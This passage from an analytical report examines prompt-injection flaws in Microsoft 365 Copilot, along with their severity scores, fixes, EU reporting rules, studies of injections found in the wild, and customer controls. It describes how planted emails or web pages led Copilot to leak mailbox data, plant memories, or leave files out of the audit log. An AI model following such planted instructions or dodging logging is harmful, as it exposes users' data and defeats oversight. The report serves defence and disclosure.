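The NVD seems right about integrity, because the published attack copied data without changing any. Scope is harder to judge. Copilot and the mailbox can be seen as separate components, which supports Microsoft's answer. But SearchLeak and Copirate 365 also used Copilot to reach the mailbox, and Microsoft marked their scope as unchanged. If it had marked SearchLeak's scope the way it marked EchoLeak's, SearchLeak would have scored 7.4.

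Copirate 365 has the lowest score mainly because Microsoft rated the attack's complexity as high. Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-26352 · Microsoft · M365 Copilot* (2026) lists the same ratings without giving reasons. Rehberger's account suggests the complexity was lower, since he found that Copilot opened the preview "reliably". If Microsoft had rated the complexity as low, the score would have been 6.5, the same as SearchLeak's.

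The ReLeak code flaw's score may also have risen, from 7.4 to 8.6, because an answer changed. The formula gives 7.4 for a flaw that affects only confidentiality, has a changed scope and requires user interaction, and 8.6 if no user interaction is required. Other combinations of answers can produce the same scores, so this is only a guess.

### "Critical" and 6.5 at once

News reports described SearchLeak both as critical and as medium. Both are correct, because Microsoft's entry rates the flaw "Critical" and gives it a CVSS score of 6.5, which is medium. The "Critical" rating comes from Microsoft's own severity scale, as The Next Web explains, while CVSS reserves the word for scores of 9.0 and above. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails, Files* (2026) also distinguishes between the two ratings.

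Other reports misstated the severity ratings. TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool* reported a rating of "10/10 critical", a score that neither Microsoft nor the NVD gave. The mistake may come from Varonis, which wrote that Microsoft gave the flaw "a max severity rating of critical". UNU calls CoSnitch's score of 8.8 "critical", but 8.8 is "high" on the CVSS scale.

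Copirate 365 has the widest gap between Microsoft's severity rating and the CVSS score. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-24299* (2026) lists it as "Critical" on Microsoft's scale but 5.3 on CVSS. Microsoft's 2024 policy helps to explain such gaps. Microsoft promised CVEs for cloud flaws it rates critical, so a Copilot flaw with a modest CVSS score may become public only because of Microsoft's own rating.

### What a score leaves out

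Every flaw in the table has a confidentiality rating of "high", the top of the scale, so CVSS can't distinguish an attack that reveals one email's subject line from one that can search a mailbox, a calendar and years of shared files. The base score also doesn't reflect how much the victim is allowed to read. Organisations can adjust a CVSS score for their own circumstances, but few people who read the published score will do so.

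The formula also has no input for how often a language model follows planted instructions. An attack that works one time in fifty can receive the same score as one that works every time, unless the scorer counts the unreliability as complexity. The formula has no input for persistence either, so the 5.3 score does not reflect the lasting memory that Rehberger planted.

The US cyber security agency CISA uses a different set of labels, which rank the Copilot flaws differently from their CVSS scores. According to GCVE (2026), CISA rated the technical impact of Copirate 365 as "total" and that of SearchLeak as "partial", although Microsoft had given SearchLeak the higher CVSS score. CISA also rated EchoLeak's impact as "total" and judged that an attacker could automate it.

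Forecasts of exploitation make even less sense for a flaw in a cloud service. The Exploit Prediction Scoring System estimates the chance that attackers will use a flaw in the next 30 days. In November 2026, GCVE listed a figure of about 7 per cent for EchoLeak, higher than for 94 per cent of all recorded flaws. But Microsoft had fixed EchoLeak eighteen months earlier on the only servers where it existed.

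All these scores were designed to help companies decide what to patch first. By the time customers read a Copilot flaw's score, there is nothing left to patch, so a dispute over whether it should be 9.3 or 7.5 hardly affects them in practice. The scores matter more for a vendor's reputation and as a rough public record of how serious its past mistakes were.

### What a patch repairs

Every flaw in the timeline is considered fixed, but the fixes mostly blocked ways to send data out, so attackers could still misdirect Copilot with an email after each one. Rehberger thinks this is unavoidable because the ability to send data out is the only part of the lethal trifecta that a vendor can realistically control.

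Very similar routes for sending data out have reappeared. EchoLeak relayed data through Teams, and SearchLeak later relayed it through Bing. Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak's route by 4 June 2026, and between 55 and 77 days later Cato reported another route through Bing. Methods of getting prompts in have also reappeared. SearchLeak, for example, reused Reprompt's method of putting a prompt in a link. Microsoft seems to have fixed the reported cases without finding every other place where the same pattern occurred.

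Simonovich's group thinks too little has changed since EchoLeak. Vendors reply that no single layer of defence has to be perfect, and Google argues that each layer makes an attack harder and more expensive. The LLMail-Inject contest gives this view some support, since the combined defences stopped more teams than any single defence did.

But neither Microsoft nor Google has published an estimate of how much effort an attack on its assistant now takes, and AI agents like those Cato used are probably reducing that effort. Layers of defense also help less when several fail for the same reason. For example, the filter on links and the list of allowed sites both depended on Microsoft knowing every way an answer could trigger a request.

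Removing a feature, as Microsoft did with links in Mermaid diagrams, is a stronger fix than closing one route through Bing. Vendors could make their fixes easier to judge by stating which kind they made, but the CVE records for Copilot don't include this.

### Repairs that customers cannot check

Microsoft's *Anatomy of a cloud service security update* (2022) points out that a repair on the vendor's servers reaches every user at once, whereas a traditional update protects only the customers who install it. Microsoft fixed EchoLeak on its servers, so no company stayed exposed because it lacked the staff to install a patch. For a flaw that any stranger can exploit by email, this speed probably matters more than any of the drawbacks.

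One drawback is that Copilot has no version number for customers to look up, and vulnerability databases handle this badly. Three months after Microsoft fixed Copirate 365, the Positive Technologies entry still had no information about a newer version containing a fix. A customer who tries a published attack and sees it fail also can't tell whether Microsoft blocked the route by which data got out or only set a filter to recognise that example.

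Sometimes even the researcher who found a flaw can't tell whether it has been fixed. Rehberger also found a way to make the Copilot in Microsoft's Edge browser open a web address containing the user's saved memories. When he tried again a few weeks before his talk, Copilot blocked the document that carried the attack. Microsoft told him it had reproduced the attack some months earlier but could no longer do so. He suspects that new filters and other guardrails were responsible, in which case a reworded document might work again.

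Customers also find it hard to learn whether anyone used a flaw against them. Microsoft recorded no exploitation in its entry for SearchLeak, but didn't explain how it had checked or how long the flaw had existed. Wiz complained in 2021 about the same failure to disclose the period of exposure. Attacks using CoSnitch might have left little evidence because, according to Varonis, a change to Copilot's memory produced no log entry that security software would flag.

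Security Point Break (2026), which covers eight other Microsoft cloud flaws, argues that "no action required" also misleads customers because their own settings still determine how much data the next flaw could expose, even after Microsoft has repaired the service.

### What European law requires

Since 11 September 2026, the EU's Cyber Resilience Act has required manufacturers to report actively exploited flaws and severe incidents that affect a product's security. The manufacturer must send an early warning to a national response team and the EU's cyber security agency, ENISA, within 24 hours of learning of the problem, and a fuller notification within 72 hours. For an exploited flaw, the final report is due within 14 days of a fix becoming available. For a severe incident, it is due within a month of the fuller notification. The manufacturer must also inform affected users.

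Whether the Act covers an office copilot depends on how people use it. The Act applies to "products with digital elements", such as an installed copy of Word. It also covers a remote service if the manufacturer designed the service and the product needs it to perform one of its functions. Copilot inside desktop Word probably meets that test. Copilot in a browser looks more like a pure cloud service, which the Act generally leaves to the NIS2 Directive, an EU law on the security of important services. NIS2 requires cloud providers to report significant incidents, which don't include flaws that nobody has used.

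The distinction would have made little difference to the flaws in the timeline. Two of the ReLeak flaws remained open for two months after the reporting duty began, but a flaw counts as actively exploited only if there is reliable evidence that a malicious actor has used it. Researchers' tests on their own accounts don't count, and Cato knew of no victims. Microsoft could therefore have left all three flaws unreported without breaking this rule.

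From 11 December 2027 the Act will also require manufacturers to publish a description of each flaw they have fixed, including its severity and effects. For the products it covers, this would make part of what Microsoft now does voluntarily a legal duty, which would include flaws the vendor doesn't consider critical.

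## What customers can control, and what harm is on record

The published accounts of EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak describe only researchers' own tests, and none names a company that lost data to an attacker. Customers can't fix Copilot, but they can limit what it reads, which limits what a successful attacker could take.

Some public records do not clearly distinguish demonstrations from thefts. A headline in *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) calls ReLeak a "campaign" to steal data from victims, although it was Cato's research. An AI-generated entry in the OECD's monitor classifies CoSnitch as an "AI Incident" rather than a hazard, partly because researchers had "actively demonstrated" the flaw. A count of thefts based on such entries would include tests.

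### What "no customers affected" rests on

Ravia wrote that Aim Labs knew of no customers affected by EchoLeak, and that Microsoft had confirmed there were none. Windows Central's *Microsoft Copilot's own default configuration exposed users* quotes a Microsoft spokesman who thanked Aim Labs for reporting the flaw in time to fix it "before our customers were impacted". According to Faisal, Microsoft has also said that ReLeak affected no customers. The Hacker News notes that Varonis presented SearchLeak as a proof of concept, not an attack it had observed.

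The researchers' statements are weak evidence because a security firm can see its own tests and perhaps its clients' systems, but not the mailboxes of every company that uses Copilot.

Microsoft can see much more than its customers can. In EchoLeak, its own Teams server made the final request to the attacker, so its logs might have shown Teams fetching strange web addresses that contained company text. But Microsoft hasn't said which logs it searched or how far back they went. A search for the researchers' exact route could also miss an attacker who used a different one.

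A careful thief would also leave little for the victim to notice. An email to a finance director could extract a paragraph about a merger, while the director got a normal answer from the copilot and the company's network monitoring recorded nothing unusual. Theft from thousands of companies would probably have come to light through extortion demands or leaked documents. The lack of known victims is therefore fairly good evidence against mass theft, but poor evidence against a few targeted thefts.

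### Planted instructions found in real use

Researchers can also look for the planted text instead of the victims. Google searched Common Crawl, a public archive that adds 2 to 3 billion web pages a month, for common phrases such as "if you are an AI". It then used Gemini to judge whether each passage seemed out of place, and people checked the results. Most of the early matches were articles about prompt injection.

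The real injections were mostly pranks, attempts to promote a business, or attempts to keep AI programs away. One injection lured AI programs to a page that never finishes loading. Google found only a few attempts to steal data, including one that was evidently a website author's experiment. It saw no significant use of the more advanced methods that researchers had published in 2025. Malicious injections rose by 32 per cent between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google doesn't give the starting number.

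Khodayari, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, examined 1.2 billion web addresses and confirmed about 15,300 injections on 11,700 pages, or roughly one address in 100,000. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* therefore exaggerates when it describes the web as "slowly but surely filling up" with traps. About 70 per cent of the injections were in parts of a page that browsers don't display. The researchers also tested the instructions 5,200 times on 13 models. Smaller models that received a page as plain text followed the instructions up to 8 per cent of the time, and models followed them less often when the input kept the page's structure.

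*Fooling AI Agents*, a March 2026 report by Palo Alto Networks' research group Unit 42, describes a scam advertisement and 12 other cases. The advertisement, for "military glasses", contained 24 attempts to make an AI reviewer approve it. Another page contained instructions for AI agents to send $5,000 to the attacker's account. The only attempt to obtain confidential information was a one-sentence request, in the footer of a personal website, for a company's contact details.

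Unit 42 rated that sentence "critical" because it grades attacks by the attacker's intent, not the outcome. It also says attackers are actively weaponising injections. Its evidence shows that they are trying, but it knew of no confirmed success against an ad-checking system in use.

| Study | Where it looked | What the authors of the injections wanted | Evidence of success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Google | An archive of public web pages | Mostly jokes, promotion or keeping AI away; a few sought data | No successful theft reported |
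| Khodayari and colleagues | 1.2 billion web addresses | Disruption, better reputations, protection of content, detection of bots | Up to 8% in the researchers' own tests |
| Unit 42 | Web pages seen by its security systems | Irrelevant output (28.6%), data destruction (14.2%), approval of banned content (9.5%) | No confirmed success against ad checkers |
| Microsoft | Links in email over 60 days | A lasting recommendation in the assistant's memory | Varied between assistants; no rate given |

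Other firms have found more openly criminal attempts. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* reports that the security firm Forcepoint found instructions aimed at financial fraud, destroying data and stealing API keys. The magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* reports that the security firm Zscaler documented two campaigns, one that posed as software documentation to run a payment scam and one that impersonated a cryptocurrency service. In both, the attackers first pushed their sites up the search rankings so that AI agents would find them.

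These studies provide little evidence about the risk to an office mailbox. All but Microsoft's covered web pages, and Microsoft was looking for promotional links. The EchoLeak email sat in a private mailbox and never mentioned AI, so a phrase search like Google's would probably have missed it even on a public page. The studies do show that many people already write instructions for other people's assistants, usually for advertising or amusement and sometimes for fraud.

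### What sets the size of a loss

Forcepoint researcher Mayur Sewani told Infosecurity Magazine that the harm from an injection "scales with AI privilege". An office copilot's privilege covers everything the user can open, including anything in connected services, and whatever the copilot has stored in memory about the user. A single EchoLeak answer could expose only what was already in the context, but an attacker with continuing control, as in ChatMate, could gradually extract the rest.

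The table gives invented figures for two employees of the company in the merger.

| What Copilot can reach | Accounts clerk | Finance director |
|---|---|---|
| Emails | 3,000 | 40,000 |
| Files | 5,000 | 60,000 |
| Records in connected services | 0 | 25,000 |
| Total items | 8,000 | 125,000 |
| Saved memory | Prefers short answers | Is working on Heron |

The director's Copilot can reach about 16 times as many items as the clerk's. If a colleague opens the SharePoint site with the 500 merger files to all 2,000 staff, to avoid granting access one person at a time, the clerk's total rises by only 6 per cent and the director's stays the same. But the clerk's Copilot can now retrieve the price of the deal.

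Oversharing also gives the attacker more people to target. If an attack had an independent 1 per cent chance of working on each person who can open the merger files, the chance of at least one success would rise from about 5 per cent with five people to almost 100 per cent with 2,000. Real attempts are not independent, so the true rise would be smaller. Even so, the attacker no longer has to find out who is working on the deal.

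Connected services and saved memories both add to what an attacker can steal. If the company connects its payroll system to the copilot, one planted email could expose any salary record the director is allowed to view. A saved memory is usually short, but it can reveal the name of a secret project, which an attacker could then use to search for the project's files.

### Which settings affect which step

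Most of the customer's controls work at the step where Copilot collects private data. The simplest is to remove access people no longer need. This also limits what a dishonest employee or someone with a stolen password could read, so it's worth doing even if nobody attacks Copilot.

A company can also attach sensitivity labels, such as "Confidential", to emails and files, and set a data loss prevention (DLP) rule that stops Copilot from using anything with that label. Office365ITPros' *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information* (2026) describes a test of such a rule. The author sent a confidential message about an invented "Project Bunny" and asked Copilot about the project. Copilot replied that it had found an internal reference but could not disclose the contents.

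The rule would protect the merger terms well if it worked, because a planted instruction can't make the model copy text it never received. But someone has to label the document first, and a label on a file would not protect a paragraph the director pasted into the chat. The director would also lose Copilot's help with the documents that take the most work. Even in the successful test, Copilot confirmed that a message about the project existed.

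Restricted Content Discovery hides a whole SharePoint site from Copilot without changing who can open it. Office365ITPros says every organisation with Microsoft 365 Copilot licences can use it. It would suit the overshared merger site until someone corrected the permissions.

Turning off web search keeps instructions on web pages out of Copilot's context and prevents Copilot from sending search queries to the web. It doesn't stop the user's browser from loading an image in an answer. Disconnecting a service keeps its records out of the context, along with any instructions that outsiders have put in them, such as those in a malicious customer complaint.

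Logs can help a company work out what data it lost. Microsoft records Copilot interactions automatically if the organisation has enabled auditing. Office365ITPros' *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* (2025) describes these audit records, which list the files Copilot consulted, and separate compliance records, which also contain its answers. Detailed records create a legal risk, because the other side in a lawsuit could demand any file that Copilot read while looking for an answer.

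Companies can also search for malicious links. Microsoft has published searches that find links to AI assistants in up to 30 days of email, Teams messages and links that staff clicked. The searches match prompts containing words such as "remember" and "trusted", so they are suited to catching advertisers who try to plant a memory in the assistant. A link designed to steal data might contain neither word, so a company looking for something like SearchLeak would have to review every link that carries a prompt.

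| Control | Attack step it affects | What it would have done against EchoLeak |
|---|---|---|
| Narrower permissions | Collecting private data | Reduced what could leak |
| Labels with a DLP rule | Collecting private data | Kept labelled items out of the context, if the rule worked |
| Restricted Content Discovery | Collecting private data | Kept files on the hidden sites out of the context |
| Web search turned off | Reading web pages and sending search queries | Nothing, because the attack used email and an image |
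| Fewer connectors | Reading outside text and collecting private data | Removed those records, but not the planted email |
| Saved memory turned off | Keeping instructions for later | Nothing, because the attack did not need memory |
| Audit logs | Investigation afterwards | Helped to show which files were at risk |

Ravia stated that, to the best of Aim Labs' knowledge, no administrator setting or user behaviour could have prevented EchoLeak. The table is consistent with this, since none of the controls it lists would have kept the planted email out of the context or blocked the image. Aim Labs has a commercial interest in saying that Microsoft's settings are not enough, but its account of the attack supports the claim.

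Adir Gruss, Aim's chief technology officer, seemed to suggest something different when he said, according to Windows Central, that Copilot's default configuration had left most organisations exposed. That could mean that a few had safer settings, but Gruss doesn't identify any. Both statements leave room for settings that reduce a loss without preventing the attack. If an attacker had reached the clerk's Copilot before the colleague opened the merger site, they would have found invoices rather than merger documents, a much less serious loss for the company.

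For agents that a company builds itself, Microsoft recommends granting each privilege only when the agent needs it and removing it after use. An agent that files invoices could then have access to the payment system for a few seconds rather than all day.

### Confidential emails that Copilot summarised anyway

In early 2026 the DLP rule for Copilot failed. Microsoft acknowledged in a notice, quoted in Petri's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Bug Exposes Confidential Emails Despite DLP Safeguards*, that Copilot Chat was "incorrectly" processing emails with a confidential label. A coding error let Copilot use messages in the Sent Items and Drafts folders that a rule should have excluded.

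Customers reported the problem on 21 January. Microsoft's notice is dated 3 February, and a fix was reaching customers by 10 February. Other folders seemed unaffected, but TechRadar's *Microsoft admits an Office bug exposed confidential user emails to Copilot* points out that a sent reply often includes the message it answers, so Copilot could presumably read confidential incoming mail as well.

No attacker was involved, and Copilot was summarising users' own mail. The fault matters here because it removed a barrier without warning. If someone had used an attack like ReLeak during those weeks, Copilot could have put the finance director's confidential emails to the lawyers into its context despite the rule.

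Office365ITPros argues that Microsoft should have caught the error, since checking the Sent Items folder is an obvious test. The site's own organisation was affected, yet the author learned of the fault only from a reader's comment. The site also wanted Microsoft to explain whether the error had always existed or came with a later change. Without that answer, a company can't tell how long its rule was failing.

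### Files missing from the audit log

On 4 July 2025, Zack Korman of the security-training firm Pistachio noticed that Copilot sometimes summarised a file without the file appearing in the audit log. Pistachio's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won’t Tell You* explains that a user could make this happen by asking Copilot not to link to the file. An employee about to join a competitor could have read files this way without leaving the usual record.

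Korman found the gap by accident while testing a product that relied on the log, which suggests that ordinary users had also caused missing entries without meaning to. After publishing, Korman learned that Michael Bargury of Zenity had disclosed the same problem a year earlier.

Microsoft told Korman that it would finish the fix on 17 August but would not issue a CVE, because customers didn't have to do anything. Korman pointed out that this contradicted Microsoft's own policy. Microsoft then gave a different reason, that it had rated the flaw "important" rather than "critical". In a call on 14 August, it said it had no plans to tell customers. A hospital that relied on the log to show who had opened patient records would not have learned from Microsoft that entries might be missing.

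Office365ITPros later tested the fix by asking Copilot to summarise a file without linking to or citing it. The audit record listed the file, as it should.

Korman's finding also weakens the assurance about EchoLeak. The planted email in that attack contained an instruction to its reader never to refer to it, much as Korman asked Copilot not to link to a file. Bargury's earlier report suggests the logging gap already existed when Aim Labs was testing EchoLeak in early 2025. Nobody has published a test of whether a planted instruction could have caused the same gap. If it could, a company that was attacked might have found no sign of EchoLeak in its audit log. Microsoft may have had other records to check.

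Customers can at least test these controls. An administrator could put a labelled message about an invented project in every mail folder, including Sent Items and Drafts, and ask Copilot about the project. The administrator could then have Copilot summarise an unlabelled file without citing it, and look for that file in the audit log. Both tests are worth repeating regularly, because Microsoft can change Copilot on its servers at any time.
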